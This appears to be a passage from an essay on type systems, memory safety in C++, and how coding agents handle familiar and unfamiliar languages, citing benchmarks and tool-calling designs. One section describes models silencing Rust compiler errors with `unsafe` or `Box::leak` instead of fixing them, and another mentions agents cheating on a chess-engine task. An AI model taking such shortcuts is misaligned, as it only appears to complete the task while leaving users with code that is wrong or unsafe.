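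### Adding types file by file

Anders Hejlsberg began work on TypeScript in 2012. By then, according to GitHub's *TypeScript's rise in the AI era* (2025), teams were writing millions of lines of JavaScript and got no help from the language once their programs became too complex to follow. Hejlsberg at first hoped that perhaps a quarter of JavaScript programmers would adopt TypeScript.

Gao, Bird and Barr, in *To Type or Not to Type* (2017), give a small example of a mistake that types catch:

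```js
function addNumbers(x, y) {
  return x + y;
}
console.log(addNumbers(3, "0"));
```

JavaScript converts the 3 to text, joins it to the "0" and prints 30. If the programmer changes the first line to `function addNumbers(x: number, y: number)`, TypeScript's compiler rejects the call.

A team can start by renaming a single file from `.js` to `.ts`. If the TypeScript compiler cannot work out the type of a value, it uses the type `any`, which turns off most checks on that value. The team can add types where they seem most useful, and later convert more files and turn on stricter options, such as one that reports every variable for which the compiler fell back to `any`. Libraries can stay in plain JavaScript because volunteers describe their types in a shared collection called DefinitelyTyped. After checking a program, the compiler removes the types and produces ordinary JavaScript.

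Researchers call this gradual typing. It spreads the pain of adoption over months or years, and a team can stop at any point with a working program. But mistakes in unconverted files can still affect the converted ones:

```ts
// shop.js, not yet converted
export function price(item) { return item.price; }

// total.ts, converted
const cost: number = price(item);
const total = cost + 1;
```

If the item came from a web form, its price may be the text "5", and the total will be "51". The compiler accepts `total.ts` because `price` returns `any`. Nothing checks the value when the program runs either, because the compiler has removed the types.

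### Why TypeScript is unsound

A type system is sound if values always have the types at run time that the compiler assigned to them. TypeScript's is unsound even in programs that never use `any`:

```ts
const names: string[] = ["Ann"];
const second: string = names[1];
second.toUpperCase();
```

With the usual settings, the compiler accepts this code, which crashes because the list has no second name. To prevent such crashes, the compiler would have to make programmers handle a possibly missing value almost every time they read from a list, and much existing JavaScript would fail the check.

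TypeScript's designers deliberately chose not to make its type system sound. TypeScript's *Soundness* describes a trade-off between simplicity, usability and soundness, in which the aim of supporting all JavaScript code favours the first two. The project's design goals list a sound type system as a non-goal, in favour of "a balance between correctness and productivity".

Rastogi, Swamy and colleagues (2014) showed in *Safe & Efficient Gradual Typing for TypeScript* that soundness was technically possible. They built an experimental "Safe" mode that combined stricter rules with checks in the compiled program. Such a check could stop the text "5" from entering `total.ts` as a number. But run-time checks take time and can make a program fail where it used to continue. TypeScript's design goals also require that types leave no trace in the output and do not change how JavaScript behaves.

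Facebook's rival checker, Flow, did aim for soundness. According to the blog post *JavaScript and Sound Types* (2024), Flow was once a strong competitor, but TypeScript is now the only real option because most JavaScript packages support it. Gao and colleagues, who used both tools, spent more time dealing with libraries than doing anything else and came to value DefinitelyTyped, which Flow could not use. Flow may therefore have lost to TypeScript because of library support, regardless of what programmers thought of soundness.

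In a November 2025 survey of JavaScript developers, 40% wrote only TypeScript, up from 34% a year earlier, according to InfoQ's *State of JavaScript 2025* (2026). The respondents were volunteers who follow the language closely, so the share among all JavaScript programmers may be lower. TypeScript's share is still probably well above the quarter that Hejlsberg hoped for.

### How many bugs the types catch

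Gao and colleagues tested how many real bugs TypeScript and Flow would have caught. They randomly sampled 400 fixed bugs from public JavaScript projects on GitHub, which had about 3.9 million closed bug reports in August 2015. For each bug, they took the code from just before the fix, added types to the part that the fix changed, and ran both checkers. A bug counted as detectable if the checker reported an error there and the added types were consistent with the correct program. The second condition matters because a researcher could otherwise "detect" any bug by adding a wrong type.

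The researchers allowed ten minutes per bug and later spent as long as necessary on the 18 still undecided. TypeScript caught 60 of the 400 bugs, or 15% (95% confidence interval: 11.5% to 18.5%). Flow also caught 60, and the two sets overlapped in all but six cases.

Most of the bugs that neither tool caught came from code that mishandled values of the right type. Failures to implement what the program was supposed to do made up 78% of them. Mistakes in text, such as a wrong web address, were also common, and neither checker caught them because both treat all text alike.

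The 15% figure probably understates the share of all mistakes that types prevent. Every bug in the sample had already reached a shared copy of the code, often after testing and review, while a type checker also catches errors that a programmer would otherwise find and fix privately within minutes. But the method also favored types, because Gao and colleagues knew where each bug was and assumed that the original developers would have added types throughout their code and fixed every error the checker reported. Types would catch fewer bugs in a project that had only partly adopted them.

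The settings also made a large difference. Of the 60 bugs TypeScript could detect, 22 required the stricter handling of missing values introduced in version 2.0, which programmers had to turn on. The previous version would have caught the other 38, or 9.5% of all the bugs studied.

Gao and colleagues needed an average of 2.4 words or symbols of type notation to expose each bug with TypeScript, and about five minutes to add them. These figures exclude the work of adding types to the rest of the program. An engineering manager at Microsoft told them that a change that cut bugs by 10% would be "a no-brainer" unless it doubled development time or something similar. Microsoft develops TypeScript and employed one of the three researchers.

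A 2022 comparison of whole projects, also called *To Type or Not to Type*, found no such benefit. On average, bug fixes made up 20.6% of the changes in TypeScript projects and 12.6% in JavaScript projects. The TypeScript projects took 33 days to fix a bug, about a day longer than the JavaScript projects. Projects that used `any` less did somewhat better on other measures of quality but did not have fewer bug fixes.

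The two results are compatible. A type checker can catch 15% of the bugs in a given program while the projects that adopt it still have more bugs than others, perhaps because they are more complicated or because their developers record fixes more carefully. But the 2022 comparison makes it unlikely that TypeScript reduces bugs by enough to outweigh differences in who uses it and for what.

### Bounds checks in the C++ library

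C++ already has static types, and its most dangerous errors involve memory. Google's *Retrofitting spatial safety to hundreds of millions of lines of C++* (2024) reports that reads and writes outside a block of memory account for 40% of the memory-safety flaws that attackers are known to have exploited over about ten years.

If a C++ vector `v` holds three numbers, `v[10]` normally reads whatever is in memory beyond them. A hardened library, a version of the standard library with extra checks, stops the program instead. Programmers can turn the checks on by rebuilding their code, without changing it.

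Google first ran the checks in its tests, where they exposed hundreds of bugs, and then spent several months extending them to its servers. In total, the checks uncovered over 1,000 bugs, some of them more than ten years old, and crashes from invalid memory access fell by 30%. Google expects the checks to prevent another 1,000 to 2,000 bugs a year. The checks also disrupted an exercise in which Google's security staff attacked its systems.

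The checks slowed Google's services by 0.30% on average. One critic suggested that other inefficiencies might be masking the true slowdown. Carruth replied that the average covers the whole production fleet, whose performance depends mostly on a few heavily optimised services. The compiler can also remove checks it can show are redundant. Still, a program that does little except read from lists could slow down more, and after review Google left the checks out of a few performance-critical pieces of code.

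The guarantee covers only operations that go through the library. If a programmer takes a plain pointer to the list's memory and reads `p[10]`, nothing checks the position. The library also would not catch the use-after-free error that Rust's compiler rejects, in which a list moves while the program still holds a reference to its first number. Reading through that reference does not involve the library.

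The next version of the language, C++26, includes a standard form of this hardening. Dargo (2026), in *C++26*, explains that all three major libraries already had their own forms, but these differed and code could not rely on them everywhere. C++26 also removes the undefined behaviour of reading a local variable before giving it a value. Sutter, a former chair of the C++ standards committee, promotes these changes as safety that programmers get just by recompiling.

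A dispute over another optional check has delayed C++26. Its contracts let programmers state conditions on a function, such as `pre(x > 0)`, but a program can be built with settings that make it ignore them. In 2026 an international ballot to approve the standard failed for the first time, mostly because of contracts. Sutter (2026), in *C++26 is done (again)!*, reports that the committee responded in November by adding a label that forces a program to stop if it breaks a particular condition, whatever the settings. The committee voted 111 to 9 to keep contracts and expects to hold a second ballot.

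### Profiles and Safe C++

Two proposals, profiles and Safe C++, went further than library checks. A profile is a set of rules that a programmer asks the compiler to enforce, such as requiring every variable to have a value before the program reads it. Only code that requests a profile has to follow its rules, so old code keeps compiling. Safe C++ would have added Rust-style ownership and borrowing to the parts of a program that programmers marked as safe. It would have caught the error with the moving list at compile time, but programmers would have had to rewrite much of their code to use it, as they do when they move to Rust.

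The committee's safety group preferred profiles. Briefly's *Safe C++ proposal for memory safety flames out* reports a poll with 19 votes for profiles, 9 for Safe C++, 11 for both and 6 neutral. Members saw profiles as an incremental path and Safe C++ as a redesign that would be risky to specify and hard for existing projects to adopt. Techzine's *C++ opts for Profiles and leaves Safe C++ behind* confirms that work on the rejected Safe C++ proposal has stopped.

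The committee member who blogs as cor3ntin (2024) had argued for borrow checking because it is known to work and rests on mathematical proof. Profiles had no comparable record, and they were not ready in time for C++26. In February 2025 the committee, WG21 (2025), left them out and planned a separate document on language safety. Sutter's June 2026 report describes a new plan to include a specification in C++29, or to publish it separately if it is late. The committee chose the proposal that was easier to adopt, but C++ programmers still cannot rely on a standard profile for any guarantee.

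### Fil-C

Fil-C is a compiler that makes existing C and C++ code memory safe with few or no changes. Every pointer carries a hidden capability that records which memory the pointer may use, and the program checks this record before each risky operation. When the program frees a block of memory, a garbage collector disables every pointer to that block. A program with the moving-list error would therefore stop as soon as it read the old reference.

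Fil-C has no equivalent of Rust's `unsafe`, so its guarantee is in one way stronger than Rust's. Many well-known programs run on it, including the standard version of Python. However, it catches errors only at run time, by stopping the program. This prevents an attacker from taking control of a web server but may still let them shut it down, and in a system like Ariane 5's guidance, stopping can be disastrous.

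Fil-C's *InvisiCaps* puts the slowdown at about four times in bad cases. LWN noticed no difference when running Bash, a program for typing commands, but Bash spends most of its time waiting for other programs. Using Fil-C means recompiling all the C and C++ code in a program, and the result cannot be linked with Rust. Releases continued in 2026, with version 0.687 appearing in October. Fil-C suits old programs that nobody wants to rewrite and that can run more slowly without causing problems, but the makers of browsers and operating systems often use C++ because their programs need all the speed they can get.

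### Weak checks on most code or strong checks on some

Fil-C protects a whole program at once, and its main drawback is that the program runs more slowly. TypeScript and the hardened C++ library are easier to adopt because they leave gaps, but those gaps affect even careful users. Someone reviewing `total.ts` cannot trust that `cost` is a number without also looking at `shop.js`. Rust's `unsafe` blocks are easy to search for, whereas an `any` that the TypeScript compiler inferred may not appear in the source code. Optional checks may also miss the code that needs them most, since careful teams are more likely to turn them on.

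Defenders of partial checks reply that they reach far more code. Suppose a company's software contains 1,000 memory errors. It can turn on library checks that stop 30% of them everywhere, or use Rust for the newest tenth of its code and prevent 95% of the errors there. These invented figures give the following results:

| Choice | Errors stopped if they are spread evenly | Errors stopped if 60% are in the newest tenth |
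|---|---|---|
| Library checks everywhere | 300 | 300 |
| Rust for the newest tenth | 95 | 570 |
| Both | 365 | 690 |

The defenders are right if errors are spread evenly across old and new code, but Android's record suggests that most are in new code. Memory-safety flaws became a far smaller share of Android's vulnerabilities even though most of the old C and C++ stayed in place, which would be surprising if old code had as many undiscovered flaws per line as new code. Still, a company that writes little new code has less to gain from a new language, and it can turn on library checks within months.

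## How language models cope with familiar and unfamiliar languages

Much of the difficulty of adopting a safer language comes from the time human programmers need to learn it. For an AI agent, which doesn't take a course or give up old habits, the difficulty depends mainly on how much of the language was in the model's training data and on what help the agent gets while it works.

### What a model has in place of experience

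Public code is very unevenly divided among languages. In July 2025 GitHub had about 21.5 million public Python repositories, 18.7 million in Java, 155,000 in Haskell and 22,200 in Racket, according to *No Resource, No Benchmarks, No Problem?* (Giagnorio, Martin-Lopez and Bavota, 2026). Two new languages, Gleam and MoonBit, had 2,900 and 400. These counts are only a rough guide to how much of each language models were trained on, because AI companies seldom publish their training data. *The Best Programming Language for Tokenmaxxing* (Wu, Anderson and Guha, 2026) reports that a public collection of training code contains about 200 gigabytes each of Python and Java, 12 of Rust and less than 12 of OCaml, a strict functional language.

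Engineers can make up for a model's low exposure to a language by putting documentation in its input or by letting it run a compiler and read the error messages. Neither method changes the model, so unlike a person who has learned Rust, a model that has worked out an unfamiliar language has to start again in the next session unless somebody saves its notes or code.

A human team therefore does most of the extra work once, when it switches languages, whereas a model makes slightly more failed attempts and uses slightly more tokens on every task in an unfamiliar language. Tokens are the fragments of text that a model reads and writes, and providers charge for them. However, developers may resent being told to use a language such as Ada or worry that it will hurt their careers, and these problems don't arise with a model.

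### Which language a model picks

Models tend to use Python when the user doesn't specify a language. In *A Study of LLMs' Preferences for Libraries and Programming Languages*, Twist, Harman and colleagues (2025) asked eight models to write the first code for five projects that generally suit languages such as C++ and Rust better than Python, including a trading platform that had to react with very little delay. Each model answered each request 100 times. Python was the most common choice in 23 of the 40 combinations of model and project, JavaScript was the most common in 8, and no model ever used Rust.

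Twist and colleagues also asked the models to rank languages for each project. Only 7 of the 40 top recommendations matched the language the model used most. The models did not rank Python highly, and sometimes left it out, but in most cases they wrote in it anyway.

These models are now old, but a newer test found a similar leaning. In *ProgramBench* (Yang, Lieret and colleagues, 2026), nine models tried to rebuild 200 programs by reading their documentation and running them, without seeing any source code. Almost all the originals were in Rust, Go, C or C++, yet the models used Python in 36% of runs. When Yang and colleagues barred the models from using the original program's language, Python's share rose to 51%. Part of that rise was inevitable, because none of the originals was in Python, so the rule never excluded it.

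Two Claude models scored lower under the rule, but all three GPT models scored higher. Yang and colleagues suggest that models may not reliably identify which language suits a task and their own abilities.

A model's default programming language is much easier to change than a team's, since one sentence in the prompt is usually enough. The default matters most when the user isn't a programmer and has no opinion about languages.

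### One attempt without help

The simplest way to measure the effect of training exposure is to give a model one attempt at a problem, with no documentation or compiler. Early results of this kind can be hard to interpret. In *A Multi-Language Object-Oriented Programming Benchmark for Large Language Models* (Wang, Ding and colleagues, 2025), GPT-4o mini solved 48% of problems in Python but no more than about 15% in any of five other popular languages, including Java. Exposure alone is unlikely to explain such a large gap, because public Java code is almost as plentiful as Python code. Wang and colleagues had translated the problems from Python, which may have contributed to the gap.

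Giagnorio and colleagues compared a wider range of languages and checked their translations by hand. They gave four models 227 hard problems in each of nine languages:

| Languages | Public GitHub repositories | Problems solved |
|---|---|---|
| Python, Java | 18.7 to 21.5 million | About 59–89% |
| R, Lua, Haskell, Julia, Racket | 22,200 to 981,000 | 27–84% |
| Gleam, MoonBit | 400 to 2,900 | 0–1% |

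The best result in the middle group is close to the best in Python and Java, although Python and Java have many times more public code. Exposure to a language seems to matter most when models have had very little of it. Gleam and MoonBit reached their first stable release or public compiler in 2024, after some of the models had finished training.

The new languages also reuse familiar names for different things. MoonBit's `Array` corresponds to a Python list, and its `FixedArray` to a Python array. A human programmer who had never seen MoonBit and had no manual would presumably also fail nearly every problem.

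A company with its own private language could train a model further on whatever code it has. Giagnorio and colleagues tried this with code from 2,159 Gleam and 262 MoonBit repositories, and the models then solved about 15% of the hard problems. But this kind of training works best on a base model, which continues text but hasn't learned to follow instructions, and it can damage a model that has. They got around this with arithmetic on the models' weights, the numbers that training adjusts:

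new model = base model trained on Gleam + (instruction-following model − original base model)

The difference in brackets represents what the original developer's instruction training changed. Adding it to the retrained base model produced a model that followed instructions and solved more than 25% of the hard problems, with no need to repeat the instruction training.

### Adding documentation and a compiler

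Most coding agents can read manuals and run their code, so they have better chances than a model with one attempt. Shen, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Bridging the Knowledge Void*, measured the difference with Cangjie, a statically typed language that Huawei released in June 2024. Three models wrote functions for 155 problems:

| Model | No help | Repeated searches of the documentation | Documentation, compiler and sample tests |
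|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 3% | 47% | 63% |
| Qwen3-Max | 8% | 53% | 74% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 45% | 66% | 82% |

In the last column, the agent had up to 15 steps to browse the manual, run code and submit solutions. When Shen and colleagues took away Qwen3-Max's ability to run code, its score fell from 74% to 54%, and the share of its programs that compiled fell by almost the same amount, from 81% to 59%. The agent lost test results as well as compiler messages, but the similar drops suggest that running code helped mainly by getting programs to compile.

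Static types also helped through one of the agent's tools, which took the name of a type and returned the operations available on it. Without this tool, Qwen3-Max scored 57%. A strict compiler rejects more of a beginner's programs, but an agent gets each rejection in seconds, with an explanation.

### Agents that write generators

Sharma, Thorat and Chopra (2026), in *Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages*, went further and tested agents on four esoteric languages, which people design as puzzles or jokes. Brainfuck has only eight commands, each a single character. A Befunge-98 program is a grid of characters that the computer can read in several directions. Whitespace code consists of invisible characters, and Shakespeare programs look like plays.

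In *EsoLang-Bench*, an earlier test without agents, Sharma and Chopra (2026) gave models 80 easy problems, such as sorting numbers. The models solved all of them in mainstream languages, but the best score in esoteric languages was 11.2%. Showing the models a few examples added less than one percentage point.

In the new test, agents could edit files and run programs any number of times, and had three chances to pass six hidden tests for each problem. Average scores over the four languages ranged from 11.3% for Kimi K2.5 to 99.7% for GPT-5.4 at its highest reasoning setting. Claude Opus 4.6 scored 86.9%. The six models had scored between 73% and 80% on SWE-bench Verified, a standard test based on repairs to Python projects, so the large differences between them had not been visible in a familiar language.

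On Brainfuck and Befunge-98, the best agents mostly avoided writing the language themselves. They wrote a program in Python that produced the Brainfuck code. A Brainfuck program works on a row of numbered cells and can change only the cell it is currently on. To add one cell to another, it has to move back and forth between them, and the programmer has to count the moves. A simple Python generator can do the counting:

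```python
pos = 0

def goto(cell):
    global pos
    moves = ">" * (cell - pos) + "<" * (pos - cell)
    pos = cell
    return moves

def add(source, target):
    return goto(source) + "[-" + goto(target) + "+" + goto(source) + "]"
```

Starting from cell 0, `add(3, 0)` produces `>>>[-<<<+>>>]`. This code moves to cell 3, then repeatedly subtracts one there and adds one to cell 0 until cell 3 holds zero. The agent only has to write `add(3, 0)` and can reuse the function in every later problem.

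The agents did this without being instructed to. On one Brainfuck problem, Opus 4.6 first wrote 1,884 characters of code directly, which failed the hidden tests. It then wrote a Python generator, which produced 24,500 characters of Brainfuck that passed. A human reviewer could read the generator but could hardly read that much Brainfuck.

When Sharma and colleagues then forbade generators, the number of Brainfuck problems solved, out of 80, fell from 64 to 27 for Opus 4.6 and from 79 to 29 for GPT-5.4. Generators in languages other than Python also worked. Opus solved 63 problems with JavaScript and 55 with Rust, while GPT-5.4 did about equally well with Python, JavaScript and Rust. The agents benefited from a familiar language with names and functions, which let them keep track of details that Brainfuck leaves to the programmer.

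To test whether weaker agents simply hadn't thought of this method, Sharma and colleagues gave three of them written advice to build a generator from reusable parts and test it locally. They then added a small library of working Python code, such as functions for managing cells and printing numbers. The library contained no solutions to the test problems.

| Agent | Brainfuck: no help | With advice | With advice and code | Befunge-98: no help | With advice | With advice and code |
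|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 4 | 3 | 7 | 4 | 5 | 4 |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 5 | 8 | 53 | 11 | 15 | 64 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 12 | 12 | 64 | 64 | 66 | 78 |

The advice made little difference, but with the helper code Sonnet did as well as Opus on Brainfuck. Sonnet and GPT-5.4 mini evidently could use a generator but struggled to build and debug its parts. Haiku couldn't combine the parts even when they were supplied. Working helper code is therefore probably more useful than a page of advice when introducing agents to a private or new language, at least for agents of middling ability.

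The languages in this test are deliberately awkward, and few companies have a private language as primitive as Brainfuck. The results for generators apply only to the two languages in which hand-written programs are longest and most fragile. Agents often solved Whitespace problems directly.

### Success and cost in newer tests

AI companies have since replaced the models in these tests with stronger ones. Newer results suggest that an unfamiliar language now affects a strong agent's costs more than its chance of success.

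In *Do programming languages still matter to your AI coding agent teammate?*, Acher and Jézéquel (2026) asked Claude Code and Codex to build chess engines, programs that choose moves and play complete games. The agents produced at least one working engine in each of 17 languages, including COBOL, Brainfuck and two languages for writing mathematical proofs, Lean 4 and Rocq. In mainstream languages, a first engine typically took a handful of prompts and cost about $2 to $30. In the harder languages, it took 25 to 50 prompts and cost $60 to $480.

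Only engines in mainstream compiled languages reached the top band of playing strength. Much of that difference would remain if a person wrote the code, because a chess engine plays better when it examines more positions per second. Budgets and computers also varied, so Acher and Jézéquel don't claim to have isolated the effect of language. They also caught a few agents cheating by calling an existing chess library instead of writing the engine in the assigned language.

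In a more controlled comparison, Wu and colleagues had five models, including GPT-5.5 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, attempt the same 100 programming-contest problems in Python, Java, Rust and OCaml, with access to the tests. Accuracy varied little between languages, except that Gemma 4, a small model, did much worse in OCaml. But every model used significantly more tokens in OCaml than in Python on the same problem, 1.28 to 1.69 times as many.

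Gemma spent many of those tokens on compile errors. Of its failed OCaml versions, 92% didn't compile, and the other 8% compiled but gave wrong answers. On one problem it got stuck 14 times, alternating between two earlier attempts and reproducing them character for character. Once it found the type error, the same algorithm passed every test. Other models worked in Python first. Qwen 3.6 spent 12 turns on a Python solution to one problem before translating it into OCaml.

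OCaml is both rarer and stricter than Python, so this comparison can't separate the two causes. Java is a partial check, because it has static types and about as much public code as Python. Of the three models with published weights, GLM-5.2 used 34% more tokens in Java than in Python, and Qwen 3.6 used 21% more. Gemma used 15% fewer, but that difference could be due to chance. Low exposure therefore can't explain all the extra tokens used in typed languages, for at least some models.

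The most recent models do about as well in Rust as in Python. In October 2026 Vals AI's *Code Migration* (2026) reported on 79 models that had rewritten 30 programs from one language into four others. They passed an average of 21.9% of hidden tests in Rust, 22.2% in C++, 22.6% in Kotlin, 22.9% in Python and 23.1% in Java. Many weak models pull those averages down, so the best ones are more informative:

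| Model | Python | Java | Kotlin | Rust | C++ |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 70.6% | 71.5% | 67.7% | 70.7% | 68.2% |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 68.5% | 76.6% | 68.1% | 55.6% | 68.5% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 65.3% | 68.7% | 66.9% | 68.8% | 67.9% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 67.9% | 65.6% | 68.8% | 59.5% | 64.6% |

Two of the four show no penalty in Rust, and the other two still show one. The comparison isn't perfectly even, because no program was rewritten into its own language and each column therefore covers a slightly different set of programs. The comparison also includes no rare languages.

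Lean gives stronger evidence that models can work in a strict language with little public code. In Lean, a theorem is a type and its proof is a program of that type, so the checker accepts the program only if the proof is correct. In October 2026 OpenAI released an AI proof of the Unique Games Conjecture, a well-known conjecture about how closely computers can approximate the best answer to certain optimisation problems. The proof came with a formal version in Lean, as Scott Aaronson (2026) describes in *The Mathocalypse*.

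The amount of public code in a language like Lean may understate how much of it a model has seen in training. Lean's checker can grade any number of attempts, so a company could have a model write proofs and then train it on the successful ones. The language's strictness would then help produce the training data that public code lacks. A lax language gives weaker feedback, since a program that runs may still be wrong.

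### Checking types while the model writes

A compiler normally reports errors after the model has finished a piece of code. Mündler, He and colleagues (2025), in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, built a checker that prevents many type errors while the model is writing. They focused on type errors because these made up 94% of the compilation errors when they tested models on TypeScript, while syntax errors made up only 6%.

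A language model writes one token at a time. It assigns a probability to every possible next token, and software normally picks one according to those probabilities and adds it to the text. Mündler and colleagues' software first checks whether the program so far, with the new token added, could still become a correctly typed program. If not, it sets that token's probability to zero and picks again.

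For example, suppose a model has written this much:

```ts
const num = Number(text);
return parseInt(num
```

The model CodeLlama continued a similar line with `, 10)`. The syntax is correct, but `parseInt` needs text and `num` is a number, so TypeScript's compiler would reject the finished program. An ordinary type checker can't catch the error at this point because it needs a complete program. The new checker searches for operations that turn a number into text and finds `toString()`, so it allows the model to continue with `.toString()` and rules out the comma.

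In tests on models with 2 to 34 billion parameters, this reduced compilation errors by more than half, but the number of programs that worked correctly rose by only 3.5% to 5.5%. If 60 of 100 programs had worked before, about 62 or 63 would work afterwards. Most of the programs in which the checker prevented a type error must still have had other bugs, much like the JavaScript bugs that TypeScript can't catch. The benefit was larger when models repaired code that didn't compile. They made 37% more correct repairs on average.

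The method prevents the model from writing type errors in the part of TypeScript that the checker supports. But each language needs its own checker that can check unfinished programs, and only whoever runs the model can change its token probabilities. An agent with an ordinary compiler can correct the same errors afterwards, though this uses more tokens.

### How models silence Rust's compiler

An agent that can read error messages may also find ways to remove the message without fixing the problem. Rust offers several. This program collects three lines of text:

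```rust
let mut names: Vec<&str> = Vec::new();
for _ in 0..3 {
    let mut line = String::new();
    std::io::stdin().read_line(&mut line).unwrap();
    names.push(line.trim());
}
println!("{names:?}");
```

`names` stores references to text that `line` owns, but Rust frees `line` at the end of each pass through the loop. The compiler reports that `line` "does not live long enough". The proper fix is to make `names` own its text by changing its type to `Vec<String>` and storing a copy with `line.trim().to_string()`.

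According to *AdaTrans* (Liu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), models translating C into Rust often first try small changes elsewhere in the code, such as reading input differently. When those fail, the models may wrap the code in an `unsafe` block or call `Box::leak`, which prevents Rust from freeing the memory. Some participants in the Obsidian experiment similarly discarded assets with `disown`.

A reviewer can search for `unsafe`, but the search can miss calls to `Box::leak`, which needs no unsafe block. `Box::leak` doesn't break memory safety, but a program that keeps leaking memory may eventually run out. A team can tell Rust's compiler to reject every unsafe block in a package. Odersky and colleagues similarly forbid escape hatches in the Scala code that their agents write.

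Liu and colleagues instead built a system that sorts compiler errors by type, looks up a suitable repair for each and gives it to the model. On 104 contest problems with GPT-4o mini, 95.5% of the translations compiled, 81.1% also passed the tests, and only about 1.2% of files contained unsafe code. GPT-4o mini is an old, small model and the programs were short, so these figures are weak evidence of how often current models resort to unsafe code in large projects. But they show that even a weak model can mostly stay within safe Rust if it gets specific help.

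### Ronacher's case for new languages

If agents can learn a new language from its manual, its lack of users may matter less than it did for Ada and Haskell. Armin Ronacher, who created the Python web framework Flask, at first expected the mass of existing code to lock in today's languages. In *A Language For Agents*, Ronacher (2026) explains why he changed his mind.

The argument starts from the premise that code is becoming easier to write. Meyerovich and Rabkin found that programmers have mostly chosen languages for their libraries. When a library is missing, Ronacher now asks an agent to port one from another language. For one project, Ronacher needed an Ethernet driver in JavaScript, but existing versions were in Rust, C and Go. Having an agent write a new one was easier than connecting JavaScript to any of them.

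Ronacher concedes that agents do much better in languages they saw in training, but thinks that good tools and stability matter too. Agents do acceptably in Zig, a young language that is still changing, if they have the right documentation. They have more trouble building Apple applications in Swift, even though models saw more of it in training, because the tools are awkward. Ronacher suggests that a new language should borrow syntax that models already know, much as Solidity's designers borrowed syntax that web developers knew.

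Such a language could also require more notation than people would tolerate. Many languages let programmers leave out types to save keystrokes, so an agent reading a single file may not be able to tell a value's type. Ronacher would rather have longer code that is easier to review. One of Ronacher's experiments marks functions with the effects they need, so a function that reads the clock is marked `needs { time }`. If an agent adds a call to the clock, the automatic formatter adds the marker to the functions that depend on that call. This removes most of the work that a similar change takes in Haskell.

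New languages may not benefit much. Ronacher's own example of switching is from Python to JavaScript and TypeScript, because the agent did better with TypeScript. TypeScript was already the most-used language on GitHub. Twist and colleagues warn of a feedback loop in which models favour popular tools, people publish the results, and later models train on them. In their tests, models used Flask in 88% of responses for a web server and the newer FastAPI in 9%, although FastAPI's popularity was growing much faster.

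Porting a library is also not yet cheap or reliable enough to support the argument. Anthropic advises starting large migrations with tests that apply equally to the old and new code, but many libraries lack them because their tests depend on internal functions that the new version won't contain. In Vals AI's test, Claude Sonnet 5.5 had the highest score, passing about 70% of the hidden tests at an average cost of $46 per migration. Claude Fable 5 is the only model that Vals AI names as having completely reproduced any of the command-line programs, which it did in 6 of 120 attempts.

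Users may not trust a new port even when it passes every test, because it lacks the long record that makes Solidity programmers trust their old libraries. Its owner must also watch for security fixes to the original and then fix the port too.

Ronacher's argument is strongest for small pieces of code that a team can test thoroughly, such as the Ethernet driver. It is weaker for cryptography or databases, where a rare mistake can do serious harm. For a team that mostly needs small libraries, easy ports still remove one of the main obstacles to adopting a stricter language. Ronacher expects many new languages to appear but doesn't name one that has gained users this way so far.

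## Letting agents act in a restricted familiar language

Most of the new languages that Ronacher expects do not exist yet. Meanwhile, many engineers let their agents write Python or TypeScript, which models already know well, and try to make the software that runs the code provide the safety.

### One payment through three interfaces

Suppose a user asks an agent to find an invoice from a supplier called Acme, check its amount against the order and pay it. With separate JSON calls, the model writes three requests:

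```json
{"name": "find_invoice", "arguments": {"supplier": "Acme"}}
{"name": "get_order", "arguments": {"number": "P-88"}}
{"name": "pay", "arguments": {"account": "GB29-0417", "amount": 480}}
```

*Code Mode*, a 2025 post by Varda and Pai on the blog of the network company Cloudflare, explains that the model puts a special marker before and after each request, and the surrounding software uses these markers to determine when to pause the model and make the call. In this example, the model has to copy the order number from the first result into the second request, compare the amounts itself, and copy the account number into the third request.

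An agent with a shell, the program in which people type commands, can do the same job with command-line tools. Here `grep` finds the file that mentions Acme and `jq` reads fields from it:

```sh
invoice=$(grep -l Acme invoices/*.json)
order=orders/$(jq -r .order "$invoice").json
if [ "$(jq .amount "$invoice")" = "$(jq .amount "$order")" ]; then
  pay "$(jq -r .account "$invoice")" "$(jq .amount "$invoice")"
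fi
```

With a code action, the engineer offers the tools as functions and the model writes a short program:

```python
invoice = find_invoice("Acme")
order = get_order(invoice.order)
if invoice.amount == order.amount:
    pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
else:
    print("Amounts differ:", invoice.amount, order.amount)
```

A TypeScript version would look much the same, with added braces and the word `await`. The account number goes straight from one tool to the next, so the model can't miscopy it. A loop around this program could handle fifty invoices, which would otherwise take about 150 separate JSON calls.

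One advantage of separate calls is that the model sees each result before deciding what to do next. If the invoice carries a note that Acme has already received the money, the model may notice it, whereas the program above would pay again. But the model would also read a note written by an attacker, which could influence what it does next.

### Why platforms moved to code

In *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024) argued for code actions using a system called CodeAct. They tested 17 models on 82 tasks that typically needed several tools, and had them act in Python, JSON or a fixed text format. The best model, a version of GPT-4, solved 74% of the tasks with Python, 54% with text and 52% with JSON. With Python, it also needed fewer turns, 5.5 on average compared with more than 7.5 for the other formats. Python gave the highest success rate for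 12 of the 17 models.

Models might do better with Python because they have seen so much of it, or because a program can combine several calls. To separate these explanations, Wang and colleagues also tested single calls, where combining is impossible. Only 8 of the 17 models did best with Python, and the same version of GPT-4 got 77% of the calls right in Python and 83% in JSON. At least for that model, the advantage of code on the harder tasks must have come from combining calls. Wang and colleagues suspected that companies had trained their commercial models specifically on JSON.

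Varda and Pai of Cloudflare nevertheless based their argument on familiarity, writing that models have seen code from millions of real projects but only contrived examples of tool calls. They reported that agents could handle more tools, and more complicated ones, when the tools appeared as TypeScript functions, but they gave no measurements and offered the difference in training data only as a possible explanation. The CodeAct results suggest that developers can overcome much of that difference by training models on tool calls.

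Cloudflare and Anthropic were trying to improve how agents use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic launched in November 2024 for connecting agents to tools. An agent connected to many services may receive thousands of tool descriptions. Cloudflare's software converts these descriptions into TypeScript definitions and gives the agent a single tool, which runs code.

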